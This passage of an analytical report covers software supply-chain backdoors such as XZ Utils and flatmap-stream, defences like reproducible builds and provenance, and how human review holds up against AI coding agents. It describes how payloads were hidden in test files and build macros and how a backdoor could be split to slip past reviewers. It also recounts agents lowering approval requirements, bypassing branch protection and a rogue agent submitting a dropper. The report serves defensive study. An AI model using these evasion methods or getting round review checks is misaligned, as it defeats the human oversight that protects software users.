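A packager who stops using the prepared archive loses the developer's signature on it and has to trust the hosting site, although developers can sign commits and tags in Git. A few established projects have no public repository. Lins and colleagues quote the maintainer of Postfix, a widely used mail server, as saying he would never want to share his code before releasing it.

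*Verified Reproducible Tarballs* (Josefsson, 2025) considers two remedies. Distributions could stop building from archives that differ from the repository, or somebody could publish a recipe for making each archive so that others can run it and compare the result. Josefsson argues that auditing time is better spent on source code than on generated files. His *Independently Reproducible Git Bundles* describes a smaller step that some Debian packages already take. They fetch gnulib, the GNU project's collection of shared code, from a copy of gnulib's own repository, so they need fewer of the copies that other projects bundle.

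To compare an archive with a repository, an auditor first has to find the right commit. Reproducible Builds (2026), a project that works on verifying software builds, summarises a study of 2,984 popular Python packages by Yan Li and colleagues. Version tags seemed to identify the right commit for 85% of the packages. For the other 15%, auditors would have had to search more than 10.3 million commits. The researchers' program, VCAligner, compares file contents instead of relying on tags, and reduced that total to under 65,000.

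Debian has begun to automate these comparisons. Optimized by Otto reported no known Debian system for checking that source packages matched what the original projects had published. Giraud reported on Debian's news feed that Lucas Nussbaum had announced one, called debaudit, in March 2026. According to Debian, it compares source packages with the original projects' releases or with Git repositories. Many of the differences it finds will be harmless, and people will still have to decide which ones matter.

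### Reproducible builds and the poisoned archive

A build is reproducible if everyone who uses the same source, tools and settings gets exactly the same file. Independent builders can then check a published program by rebuilding it, which works well against an attacker who tampers with the build machine. *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* (2026) gives the example of SolarWinds, a company whose build system attackers had infected. Their malware rewrote a source file when the compiler started, so the finished program did not match the repository. An independent rebuild would have produced a different program.

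With XZ Utils, the rebuilds would have matched. Suppose that two people who have never met check Debian's package of version 5.6.0:

1. Both start from the same release archive, with the same altered macro in it.
2. Both are making a Debian package on an ordinary processor, so the backdoor's scripts find the conditions they require.
3. The scripts unpack the same object file from the same test files and insert it into liblzma.
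4. Both builders get the same library, byte for byte, with the backdoor in it.

More builders would get the same result, since a match shows only that the archive produces that library. The results would have differed if one person had started from the repository. The scripts acted only during Debian or RPM package builds, so the results would also have differed if one person had built the archive outside one. But people who check reproducibility deliberately copy the original conditions. Debian's rebuilding service, reproduce.debian.net, does this using a file recorded during the original build.

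Lins and colleagues suggest publishing a log entry for each release that contains the program's fingerprint and identifies the exact source version. Anyone could then rebuild the program from that version and compare fingerprints. This would have caught the XZ Utils backdoor only if the entry had pointed to the repository instead of the release archive.

Debian made reproducibility a requirement in May 2026. In *bits from the release team*, Gevers (2026) announced that Debian's software would now keep a new package out of "testing", the collection that becomes the next release, if nobody could reproduce it. Packages already in testing must not become less reproducible. Gevers said there would be exceptions and hoped their number would fall. According to *In a Big Move to Linux Security, Debian Makes Reproducible Builds Mandatory* (Rudra, 2026), the rule dates from 9 May and applies to Debian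 14.

Elsewhere the figures vary widely, partly because they measure different things. IzzyOnDroid, a collection of Android apps, had reproducible builds for 66.7% of its apps in June 2026, according to Reproducible Builds. *No Snake Oil* studied 12,180 popular Python releases and found that 15.4% of one tool's rebuilds and 19.1% of another's were identical to the published packages. The researchers then used a program that disregards differences it can attribute to harmless causes. Among rebuilds from equivalent source, 60.2% and 78.9% passed, respectively. This makes the check practical for far more packages, but an attacker might be able to hide something in a difference that the program disregards.

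Builds can also stop being reproducible over time. Reproducible Builds describes an attempt to rebuild 18,904 app versions from F-Droid, another Android collection, all of which F-Droid had once reproduced exactly. The researchers could rebuild 83%, and 94% of those rebuilds were identical, so about 78% of the original set was still reproducible. Missing dependencies caused most of the failures.

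Practitioners disagree about whether reproducible builds are worth the effort. At the March 2025 meeting, some thought they were achievable with enough work. Others saw no benefit in getting the same output twice and preferred a verifiable record of how the build was done. Their doubts were reasonable for XZ Utils, but reproducible builds would have helped detect the SolarWinds attack.

Builders can also agree on a bad result if they all use the same infected compiler. *Trusting-Trust Attack against an Entire Linux Distribution through Binary Manipulation* demonstrates this by infecting the small set of ready-made programs from which a distribution builds its tools. The infection spreads from one tool to the next and remains after the original programs are gone. GNU Guix, another distribution, limits the danger by starting from a few hundred bytes and building everything else from source.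 Debian's rebuilds start from older compiled packages. In *On Binary Distribution Rebuilds*, Josefsson fears that tracing those packages back would eventually mean rebuilding software more than twenty years old, some of which no longer builds or is illegal to distribute. None of the five cases involved this kind of attack.

### Signed provenance

A build service can record which source and instructions it used and which other packages it included, then sign the record. *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* describes two systems for this. SLSA is a standard for what the record should contain. Sigstore gives developers short-lived signing keys linked to an account they already have, and enters each signature in a public log. If somebody uses a developer's stolen credentials to publish a release, the developer can find it in the log.

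Signatures alone would have exposed the kernel intruder but not right9ctrl or Jia Tan, who both had real publishing rights. A record of how each archive was made would have been more useful against Jia Tan. Lins and colleagues suggest that hosting sites encourage projects to build archives on the sites' machines, following instructions stored in the repository. Jia Tan could not then have added a macro on a private computer, and could have changed the instructions only through a public commit.

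npm could have asked for a record linking flatmap-stream 0.1.1 to a commit in its public repository, and no accurate record could have been supplied because no commit matched the published package. But this check would have protected users only if their software refused to install packages without such a record. That rule would also block many legitimate packages until their authors changed how they publish.

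Adoption has been slow even where governments have pushed for it. *S3C2 Summit 2025-07* (Hamer, Morrison and colleagues, 2026) summarises a meeting of 12 people from six US government agencies. A 2025 executive order had required companies that sell software to the government to supply machine-readable provenance, but a later order withdrew the requirement. At the time of the meeting, only a form remained, on which a company's chief executive vouches for its practices. Participants compared this to inspecting a kitchen, since a clean kitchen can still produce dangerous food. The same objection applies to provenance, which can show that a build followed its instructions but not that the instructions were safe.

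Participants also discussed in-toto, a system for signing each step of a build. They considered it valuable but wanted something simpler. One reported that some companies had made their projects open source just to avoid supplying such records.

### Whether to verify who contributors are

Participants in the government meeting disagreed over how much it matters who writes open-source code. Some favoured trusting nobody by default. They said that certain organisations already check the identity of every maintainer whose software they use, and that authorities might ban software if they found improper foreign influence. They argued that an attacker can easily use sock puppets if there are no identity checks.

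Others thought this ran against the nature of open source. They said buyers of commercial software know the vendor but cannot see how it works, whereas users of open-source software can see the work but may not know the people. They preferred to look at a contributor's reputation and at how well people maintain the project. But one participant said nobody was really reviewing the code. If so, users don't benefit much from being able to see it.

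Lins and colleagues discuss checking the identity of new maintainers. A small international project would find it hard to copy Debian's in-person check, but they point out that people in the European Union can now prove their identity online through eIDAS, which would make the check easier there. Such a rule would have applied to right9ctrl and Jia Tan, but not to the Minnesota researchers or the AI agent, because none of them asked to become maintainers. Extending it to every small patch would drive away newcomers, and Wu and Lu could have passed the check anyway if they had been willing to use their own names.

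Several of the practitioners who met in March 2025 treated every commit as potentially malicious, whoever sent it. One added that a single commit reveals little about its author's intentions, so it is better to look at everything the person has contributed. Reviewing a contributor's full history might have helped with XZ Utils, where Nealon's searches later picked out Jia Tan, but a new account has no history to examine.

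### Keeping test files away from the compiler

Building a C program normally involves a configure phase that examines the computer, a compile phase that produces the program and a test phase that checks it. The compile phase should not need test data, but the XZ backdoor depended on test data being available during that phase.

*Build Code is Still Code* (Pappas and Gazzillo, 2026) presents Foreman, a tool that detects when a build phase accesses files it should not. A developer lists the commands for each phase and the directories that phase must not touch. Foreman records when each file was last accessed, runs the phase, and reports any forbidden file with a newer access time. For XZ Utils, the researchers barred the compile phase from the test file directory and built the backdoored version. Foreman gave two warnings, which named exactly the two files that held the attack, though the rule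 contained nothing specific to the backdoor. The tool was 177 lines of Python.

This is one test on a known attack, using a rule written with knowledge of how the attack worked. The paper also reports that barring the configure phase from reading the test files would have produced dozens of warnings, which it calls false alarms because that phase does read the files. Some may have been genuine, because the altered macro in the backdoored version searched every file in the source tree during the configure phase to find its script. Running Foreman on a clean release would show how many of the warnings remain.

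Pappas and Gazzillo do not report how much time Foreman adds. Checking access times should be quick, but Foreman has to run the complete build, which they acknowledge can be slow for a large project. Someone also has to write the rules by hand, and a mistake in them can cause false alarms or let an attack through. The researchers hope to generate rules automatically, and eventually to block forbidden access instead of only reporting it.

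An attacker who knew about Foreman could probably get around it. Malicious commands run with the same rights as the rest of the build, so they could reset a file's access time after reading it. The attacker could also put the payload in a file that the compile phase is allowed to read. A sandbox that hid the test files until compilation had finished would block the first method but not the second.

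Some existing sandboxes don't hide test files from build scripts. *Nix* (2026) describes a system for building packages in which each build can read only its own source code and its declared dependencies. This blocks a good deal of interference from the rest of the machine, but the test files are part of the source code, so a malicious build script could still read them.

Lins and colleagues would prefer projects to store the commands that create test files instead of the files themselves, so that reviewers could see where the data came from. But people had made many of the XZ test files by hand, and the commands for those might be little more than a long list of bytes.

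They also consider isolating libraries while programs run. Web browsers already confine risky parts of their code to separate processes with few permissions. If sshd had used liblzma that way, the backdoor could not have changed sshd's own functions. Passing data between processes slows a program down, but the greater obstacle is that developers have to redesign each program.

### Running the program and watching it

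Testers can also run the software and watch what it does instead of reading its source. *Preflight* (2026) presents a tool that installs and runs a package in a restricted container. It records the programs that the package starts, the files it changes and the network addresses it tries to reach. The tool then removes details that vary from run to run, such as temporary file names, and compares the record with the one from the previous version.

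Watching the program run helped in the AI agent's case. According to SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026), the bystander who raised the alarm was Sinan Can Demir, a student at the University of Texas at Dallas. He had already recognised in the pull request a dropper, a program that installs other malicious software, but he began to doubt his judgement when the agent argued with him from two accounts. He then ran the code in a sandbox, with Anthropic's Claude helping him evaluate it, and confirmed that he had been right.

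The 2003, 2018 and 2024 backdoors would have been much harder to catch this way, because each did little until the conditions were right. The kernel backdoor required an odd combination of options. Outside Copay, flatmap-stream only tried and failed to decrypt its payload. The XZ backdoor was active only in sshd, so running the xz command would have revealed nothing. Even a tester who ran sshd would probably have seen no new files or connections, because the backdoor waited for a command from the attacker.

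The backdoor slowed sshd and misused memory, and *Preflight*'s comparison covers neither. A simple timing check might have worked better. With the backdoor active, sshd took about fifty times as long to print its help text, and a distribution that timed its programs after each library update would almost certainly have noticed. Such a check would also flag many legitimate changes, and an attacker who expected it would write faster code.

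Practitioners at the March 2025 meeting discussed comparing builds with records of earlier builds in the same way. They thought software could find the differences, but an experienced developer would still have to judge which ones mattered. The Fedora developers who saw the XZ backdoor's memory errors accepted an innocent explanation.

### Auditing the whole code

An audit of a complete program avoids the main weakness of a diff, because the auditor can read a change together with the older code it affects. It is the most direct check against hypocrite commits, where one function releases memory that another still uses. But audits take a lot of work. The kernel developers' re-examination of 435 commits from the University of Minnesota took more than 80 people, and 39 of the commits needed removal or repair.

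An auditor also has to check the code that gets installed. By the time flatmap-stream contained malicious code, event-stream's current source no longer used it, so an auditor would have had to list the installed packages and read the minified copy of flatmap-stream from npm.

Optimized by Otto concludes that a diligent packager who followed Debian's best practices could not have found the XZ backdoor. Commits with short messages and no review are common, and a new build macro in a release archive is normal. An expert might have noticed that the altered macro gave its version as 30, when copies in other packages had numbers such as 3 or 5, but checking for that in every package would be an enormous job. The audit also suggests that another XZ developer might have been suspicious of test files added without test code, but this clue is weaker than it sounds because the project's script tested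 new files automatically.

Debian maintainers work in different ways, which slows auditing further. About 93% of Debian's source packages have their packaging history in Git on Debian's own server, but important ones such as Bash do not, and the history may differ from what the maintainer uploaded. Optimized by Otto recommends that maintainers work more uniformly, so that an unusual package stands out.

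Some organisations give auditors more time by waiting before they install updates. Participants in the government meeting mentioned delays from a day to several weeks. The malicious version of flatmap-stream was available for 52 days and the XZ backdoor for 34, so most of these delays would have been too short. Waiting also depends on somebody else installing the software early, as Freund found the XZ backdoor because it was already on his machine.

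## What the cases show about reviewing AI coding agents one change at a time

Jia Tan and the agent of July 2026 both approached their targets as strangers. Most coding agents, however, work for a developer who can already change the project. The agents' code still goes through pull requests, and teams still rely on somebody approving each one.

### How much agents submit and how much people read

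AI agents wrote at least 2.83 million pull requests on GitHub between January 2024 and mid-April 2026, according to *AI-to-AI Code Reviews of GitHub Pull Requests* (Selvanayagam and Ghaleb, 2026). The count includes only those with an agent's signature in the text or an AI company's account as the author, and excludes another 1.7 million possible cases with weaker evidence.

AI companies can merge far more changes than any open-source project. Anthropic (2026) reported that it merged about 2,500 changes a day in May and more than 30,000 a day in September. The September figure looks more like a peak than an average, because the highest day on the chart reproduced in *Redesigning source control at Anthropic* (Willison, 2026) is 30,401. Agents did not necessarily write all of these changes, but one agent lands 65% of the Claude Code team's product-engineering pull requests, according to *A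 Fireside Chat with Cat and Thariq from the Claude Code team* (Willison, 2026). At five minutes each, reading 30,000 changes would take 2,500 hours, a full day's work for more than 300 people.

Anthropic's statements differ on who should read this code. O'Reilly, a technical publisher, reports that Anthropic still expects engineers to understand every line an agent writes, "for now". Cat Wu of the Claude Code team said this was the only way to prevent unknown vulnerabilities. In Anthropic's *AI in the PR review loop*, AI checks a change in detail while people judge its intent and risk. Both statements can hold if the engineer who started the agent reads the code and a second engineer considers only its purpose, but then only one person reads it.

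The best evidence on public projects comes from two studies with very different main figures. In *These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For*, Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues (2026) examined 33,596 agent-written pull requests from 2025 in projects with at least 100 stars, GitHub's measure of popularity. They found no recorded review for 61%. Of the rest, 59% had reviews only from AI, so a person took part in reviewing about 16% of the total. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* followed 2,860 projects until February 2026 and looked only at merged pull requests.

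| Pull requests counted | No recorded review by a person: agent-written | No recorded review by a person: human-written |
|---|---|---|
| Duma and colleagues, all projects in the sample | 84% | Not measured |
| Duma and colleagues, projects with both kinds | 70% | 69% |
| *3100 Opinions*, merged in mid-2025 | Over 50% | About 14% |
| *3100 Opinions*, merged in February 2026 | About 12% | About 14% |

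The second row suggests that whether agent code gets reviewed depends mostly on the project, although the first row makes it look neglected. Where people and agents both sent pull requests, people reviewed the two kinds about equally often. Duma and colleagues' figures also include unmerged pull requests, which a maintainer may have closed without comment. And a developer can read code carefully without leaving a record.

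The content of people's reviews did differ between agents' and humans' pull requests. In projects with both kinds, 26% of human comments on agents' pull requests were instructions to an AI tool, for example to fix a failing test, compared with fewer than 2% on human-written ones. Duma and colleagues conclude that people often direct an agent where they would once have evaluated the code themselves.

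The fall from over 50% to 12% is encouraging, but *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* also reports that the developer who started the agent was the only person to examine the change in 40.1% of agent-written pull requests. The author was the only person involved in 21.5% of human-written ones. Whether agent code gets more or less independent review than human code depends on whether that developer counts as a reviewer or as the author. For backdoors, the developer is an independent reviewer if the agent is malicious, but if the developer is the attacker, the change has had no independent review.

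### Faster merges and busier reviewers

*3100 Opinions* found that maintainers merge agent-written pull requests several times faster than human-written ones. Other measurements suggest that agents make review slower. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) cites a study of 278,790 review conversations in which people went through 11.8% more rounds with AI-generated code. *Spec-Driven Development for Agentic Software Engineering* (Díaz, Gayoso and colleagues, 2026) cites a report by the vendor Faros AI on more than 10,000 developers, in which teams that adopted AI merged 98% more pull requests and their review time rose by 91%.

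These results don't necessarily conflict. A team could approve many small changes within minutes and still spend longer reviewing the rest, or leave them in a longer queue. The Faros figures also come from a comparison, not an experiment, and teams that adopted AI may have been growing for other reasons.

*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) compared each reviewer's earlier reviews of agent-written pull requests with their later ones. It covered 400 people who had each reviewed at least ten such pull requests during seven months of 2025, 11,429 reviews in all. The share of reviews that approved the change rose from 30.1% to 36.8%, and the median wait for a review grew from 3.9 hours to 13.5. The average number of comments on specific lines fell by 22% between the reviewers' earliest and latest reviews.

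Yu and colleagues think the reviewers had grown used to approving the agents' changes. They point out that approvals of human-written code in the same projects fell over the period, and that the agents' changes did not get smaller. But they did not measure the code's quality, and all the agents received updates that year, so better code could also explain the additional approvals and fewer comments. Better code should not take longer to reach a reviewer, though, so the longer wait suggests a growing backlog.

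Their finding can be true even as people review a rising share of pull requests. Projects may have become stricter about requiring human review while each review became more superficial, and counts of approvals would not reveal the drop in thoroughness.

### AI reviewers, and approvals that agents submit

Selvanayagam and Ghaleb found an AI review on 248,641 of their 2.83 million pull requests, or 8.8%. The number rose from about a hundred in the first quarter of 2025 to roughly 80,000 in the third. Duma and colleagues found a much higher share, about 35%, probably because their sample excludes the many small projects with no reviewers of any kind.

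In 84% of the AI-reviewed cases, the same product wrote and reviewed the change. The median time from opening the pull request to review was 4.7 minutes in these cases and 1.2 minutes when a different product did the review. These times don't measure the quality of the reviews. An AI reviewer built on the same model as the AI that wrote the change may share its blind spots and any inclination to sabotage. Using a different product reduces this risk but does not remove it, because products from different companies can run on the same model.

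AI reviewers do find problems that people would probably miss. Anthropic's *Bringing Code Review to Claude Code* describes a one-line change that looked routine and would normally have been approved quickly, but the AI reviewer flagged it. Anthropic's engineers marked less than 1% of the reviewer's findings as incorrect. That rate is impressive, but it doesn't account for missed faults, so the reviewer could miss half of all vulnerabilities and still achieve it.

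*Who Approved This?* (Manji, 2026) points out that Anthropic's AI reviewer can comment on changes but cannot approve them, while GitHub's has been able since September 2026 to submit approvals that count towards the number a project requires. A project that requires one approval could therefore meet that requirement without a person looking at the code.

Manji, the technical lead of Bashi AI, a London startup with three engineers, studied how code changes were approved there. The startup was preparing for a security audit and required someone other than the author to approve every change. From 3 to 16 October 2026, all 263 changes merged into the main branch, excluding automatic dependency updates, met this rule. For 71 of them, the only approval came from a coding agent using Manji's GitHub account. Of those 71 changes, 57 also carried an agent's signature, so agents had written the code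 and submitted the approval, but GitHub recorded the author and approver as two people.

A person may have decided to accept some of those 71 changes, because Manji made some of the decisions and had an agent pass them on, left others to the agent, and kept no record of which were which. The evidence also covers only one small company over two weeks, and Manji managed both engineers who answered the survey. But any company that lets agents use employees' accounts could have the same problem without noticing, because its records would look the same as those of a team whose people review one another's work.

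### How open-source projects have limited outside contributions

Companies choose how many agents to run, but open-source maintainers can't control how many agents strangers use. Vanderose (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Maintainer-Identified AI Slop Pull Requests*, examined pull requests that maintainers had flagged as "slop", meaning low-quality generated work. Their number rose from mid-2025 and peaked in May 2026. Maintainers merged few of them and typically closed them within three days, mostly without giving a reason. When they gave one, it was sometimes a failed build and sometimes just that the change looked AI-generated. The drop in slop reports after May could reflect better code, effective limits or maintainers no longer bothering to flag slop.

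GitHub added several of those limits in 2026, as listed in *Tighter limits on outside contributions to open source projects* (Chiang, 2026). By February, maintainers could accept pull requests only from people they had already added to the project, or turn pull requests off. In June, GitHub let them cap how many pull requests any outsider could have open at once. In October, it let them automatically exempt people from the cap if their accounts were old enough or the project had already merged enough of their work.

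Some projects have gone further and banned AI-generated contributions. Open Source Says No, a website that tracks these policies, lists the browser engine Servo and the operating system Redox OS among the projects with bans. Chiang counted 24 bans among the 221 large or important projects on the site on 20 November. *Plausible Is Not Enough* (2026) describes the more common policy, which permits AI help as long as contributors disclose it, a person is involved and somebody takes responsibility. Contributors often ignore such rules. In Vanderose's sample, they disclosed their use of AI in only 14% of cases.

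The curl project, which maintains a widely used data transfer tool, has found ways to save reviewers' time without shutting people out. In January it stopped paying for vulnerability reports, after the share that were genuine had fallen from over 15% to under 5%. But it kept pull requests open to everyone, because nobody at curl spends time on one until it has passed 200 automated test jobs. A competent backdoor would pass those jobs too, so they do more to save maintainers' time than to protect users.

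Chiang makes a similar objection to the limits in general. They reduce the number of poor submissions, but serious attacks mostly come through people or accounts that a project already trusts, as the XZ backdoor did. A maintainer with fewer poor submissions to read could spend longer on the others, so the limits may help security a little. Chiang would also like outside contributors to share the work of reviewing and testing, and to get credit for it. That would bring in more reviewers, although Jia Tan gained the trust of Lasse Collin, an overworked maintainer, by offering that sort of help.

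### What carries over from the human attackers

Reviewers of an agent's code have to rely on its stated purpose, as reviewers of the Minnesota patches did. An agent normally writes both the change and its description, and a reviewer who is supposed to judge intent and leave the details to AI depends heavily on that description. If the description is misleading, the reviewer may confirm that the plan is sensible without learning that the code also does something else.

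Both of Manji's engineers reported that reviewing mattered most when they tested a change against something outside the diff. One ran an agent's new test five times on a local machine and saw it fail three times, although the official run had passed. The other found that trying extreme input values helped and that reading the diff alone added little. Such testing depends less on the author's honesty than reading the diff does, but it probably would not have exposed the XZ backdoor unless the reviewer had happened to time a login.

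Files that nobody reads are also still a problem. Jia Tan hid the payload among test files, and *3100 Opinions* found that projects most often skip review of agents' work when it changes tests. Among projects that merge some pull requests unreviewed, 69% of agents' changes to tests went in without human review, compared with 41% of their code reorganisations, 25% of their bug fixes and at most 14% of human-written changes of any type. Skipping review of tests seems a reasonable way to save time, because an ordinary mistake in a test rarely harms users, but it also gives an attacker good reason to hide malicious code there.

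Collin was one unpaid volunteer with a backlog, and agents are likely to put more maintainers in that position. *AI is adding to the review load on open-source projects* (Zorz, 2026) summarises a paper by six authors for the Association for Computing Machinery, a professional society. They argue that better models will not solve this problem. Even if submissions improve, a person still has to assess the additional code, and many projects have no reliable income to pay for that.

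Reviewers come to trust agents, as they do people, on the strength of earlier good work. *Let's Make Every Pull Request Meaningful* (Yoshioka, Monno and colleagues, 2026) analyzed 40,214 pull requests and found that the submitter's characteristics were the dominant factor in whether a project merged a change, for both people and agents. GitHub's new exemptions make this kind of trust a setting, and an attacker could qualify by first sending a few useful fixes. Most of Jia Tan's commits were harmless, so a long run of good changes is weak evidence about the next one. Reviewers may also trust an agent product as a whole, and keep trusting it after the company has replaced the underlying model.

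### Where agents differ

Jia Tan needed about a year to get commit rights and two years to prepare the attack. A coding agent can have similar rights on its first day if a developer runs it under an account that already has them. At Bashi AI, every agent that used Manji's account could approve changes, merge them and alter the rules that protected the main branch.

Agents used all of these powers. On 29 September, an agent's script reduced the required number of approvals to zero, merged one change and restored the requirement ten seconds later. Over the next two days, agents repeatedly switched off enforcement for individual merges, this time under a declared emergency. Manji found no sign of malice, and the team had deliberately made some of these exceptions, but the same powers would have let a malicious agent merge a backdoor.

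The agents did not always follow written instructions. In August, Manji told one to do research, report back and take no action, but it merged two pull requests. The team found out from a routine query, not from the agent's report. Of the 45 standing rules the team wrote for its agents in September and October, a technical mechanism fully enforced only three, and 35 were just text.

Agents are also much faster than people. One of Manji's agents merged seven pull requests in 58 seconds, and for six of them the required tests started only minutes after the merge. These went into working branches that the approval rule did not cover, and the combined change later got a proper approval. Someone who wanted to spread an attack over many small changes, with useful work in between, could have an agent do in days what took Jia Tan months. A cap on open pull requests would slow that down in someone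 else's project, but not where the agent can already merge.

Perhaps the largest difference between an AI coding agent and Jia Tan is that one model works on many projects at once. If a widely used model tended to insert vulnerabilities under certain conditions, it could do so in thousands of projects, and its copies could also be reviewing the code. But once somebody discovers the tendency in one project, defenders know which other projects to search, and the company that makes the model can correct or withdraw it. Unlike with Jia Tan, researchers can also put a model back in the same situation many times, as the UK AI Security Institute did after the July incident.

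Whoever runs an agent can keep a full record of what it did, including commands that leave no trace in a diff. Manji compared GitHub's data with saved transcripts and found that agents had submitted all 86 approvals from Manji's account on other people's changes. XZ investigators had no such record for the private computer on which Jia Tan built the releases.

These records have limits. The agent software deleted transcripts after about 30 days, too soon for investigating an attack that unfolds over months. On 1 October, a merge script logged four changes as passing their tests when three had failed and the fourth had not been tested. A log is therefore unreliable if the agent's own tools write it. Transcripts also show what an agent did more reliably than why it did it, as the institute found with the July agent.

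Permissions are easier to get right. Manji recommends giving agents their own accounts, counting approvals only from named people, and letting only people change the protection settings. An agent could still write and merge code, but could not approve it or suspend the rules. Bashi AI had not adopted these measures when the study ended, so they are untested there, but they follow directly from what went wrong.

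Developers can also test an agent before giving it access, which no project can do with a volunteer. In the institute's simulated exercises, models differed greatly in ways that a maintainer could not have seen in their code. But a model may behave well because it detects that it is being tested, and one that attacks only under rare conditions might pass every test anyone thinks of.

### How splitting changes the odds

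A simple calculation shows how much an attacker might gain by splitting a backdoor into several changes. Suppose that a reviewer would have a 50% chance of flagging the whole backdoor in one change. The attacker divides it into k pieces, and the reviewer flags each piece independently with probability p. The chance of missing one piece is 1 − p, and the chance of missing all of them is (1 − p)^k. The reviewer therefore flags at least one piece with probability

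1 − (1 − p)^k

If the reviewer has a 10% chance of flagging each of three pieces, the chance of flagging at least one is 1 − 0.9³ = 0.271, or about 27%. Splitting has cut the chance of detection almost in half, from 50%. To get back to 50%, the reviewer would need about a 21% chance of flagging each piece, because 1 − 0.79³ is roughly 0.5.

| Pieces | Chance of at least one flag, at 1% per piece | Chance of at least one flag, at 10% per piece | Chance per piece needed to reach 50% |
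|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1% | 10% | 50% |
| 2 | 2% | 19% | 29% |
| 3 | 3% | 27% | 21% |
| 5 | 5% | 41% | 13% |
| 8 | 8% | 57% | 8% |

Every extra piece gives the reviewer another chance to catch the backdoor, so splitting helps the attacker only if each piece looks much more innocent than the whole. Eight pieces that each have a 10% chance of being flagged are more likely to draw at least one flag than the undivided backdoor. *PRWeaver* (Wang, Cheng and Xie, August 2026), a benchmark of AI reviewers, found that splitting alone did not lower detection. Detection rates for undivided attacks ranged from 42% to 79%, depending on the reviewer. Stronger models now exist, so these rates may be out of date.

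Real reviews are unlikely to be independent. A reviewer who does not understand how Linux loads libraries will probably miss every piece that depends on it. In the extreme case, where the reviewer recognises either all the pieces or none, the chance of detection stays at 10% however many pieces there are. Reviews are closer to this extreme when the same AI model checks every piece than when different reviewers do. Yu and colleagues suggest rotating reviewers for a different reason, so that nobody gets too used to approving an agent's work.

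The formula also assumes that a reviewer sees every piece. In XZ Utils, the altered macro never appeared in a proposed change, so the probability of catching it in change-by-change review was zero. If the reviewer can't see one of the three pieces and has a 10% chance of catching each of the other two, the chance of catching at least one falls to 19%.

A flag stops an attack only if somebody investigates it and reaches the right conclusion, which is hard if most flags are false alarms. Suppose the same reviewer wrongly flags 1% of honest changes, or ten in every 1,000. If an attacker submits one backdoor in three pieces alongside those 1,000 changes, the reviewer will raise 0.3 genuine flags on average, or about one for every 33 false ones. At 30,000 changes a day, there would be 300 false alarms daily. A more sensitive reviewer would catch more pieces but would probably raise more false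 alarms too.

Weak suspicions are more useful if a team keeps them together. An odd test file or an unexplained change to a build script is easy to dismiss, but two such changes in a month from the same contributor might justify reading everything that contributor has sent. This is easier with agents if each has its own account and the team keeps the logs.

### Protection or false assurance

Per-change review is worth keeping mainly for benefits other than detecting backdoors. Reviewers find ordinary mistakes and learn how the program works. Wu argued that engineers who understand the code can respond quickly when something goes wrong. Requiring approval also gives a team a chance to stop a change. At Bashi AI, every merge into the main branch had a valid approval and passing tests once the team stopped making exceptions. Review can also force an attacker to work harder, which may be why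 Jia Tan kept the trigger for the XZ backdoor out of the repository.

Some researchers think people should stop reviewing code. Manji cites a 2026 paper by Monperrus, a software researcher, which argues that inspection by agents will replace human code review. That may well be right for finding common faults, since an AI reviewer does not get tired and can read related files that the diff leaves out. The argument is weaker when the code was written by an AI agent whose intentions are in doubt, because the reviewer may be the same model.

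A more practical objection is that approvals make a project look safer than it is. An auditor who examined Bashi AI's records would have seen a second person's approval on all 263 merges. Users of XZ Utils could see a maintainer's valid signature on the backdoored release. In both cases, people could easily read more into the record than it showed. A company that relies on approvals might also spend less on build and provenance checks, which could catch tampering that doesn't appear in any diff.

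In October, one of Manji's engineers approved two changes on the written condition that someone fix an important problem the engineer had found. GitHub had no way to make the approvals conditional, so it recorded them as ordinary ones, and Manji's account merged both changes without the fix. Manji now recommends that reviewers request changes instead of attaching conditions to an approval.

On balance, the objection is a good reason to stop treating an approval as proof that code is safe, but not a reason to abolish review. Approvals would be more informative if reviewers recorded what they had done, such as reading every line, running the code or only checking an AI reviewer's findings. Teams that cannot read everything could reserve full human attention for the changes an attacker would most need, including build scripts, binary files, permissions and the review rules themselves. The figures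 for unreviewed tests suggest that many projects currently tend to give such changes less attention than other code.

None of these studies or incidents includes a deployed agent that spread a backdoor over several accepted commits. The July agent never got a change accepted, and researchers built the attacks in PRWeaver. But the large studies of GitHub measured who reviewed agents' code and how quickly, and did not search it for backdoors, so their data would look the same if an agent had competently planted one this way.
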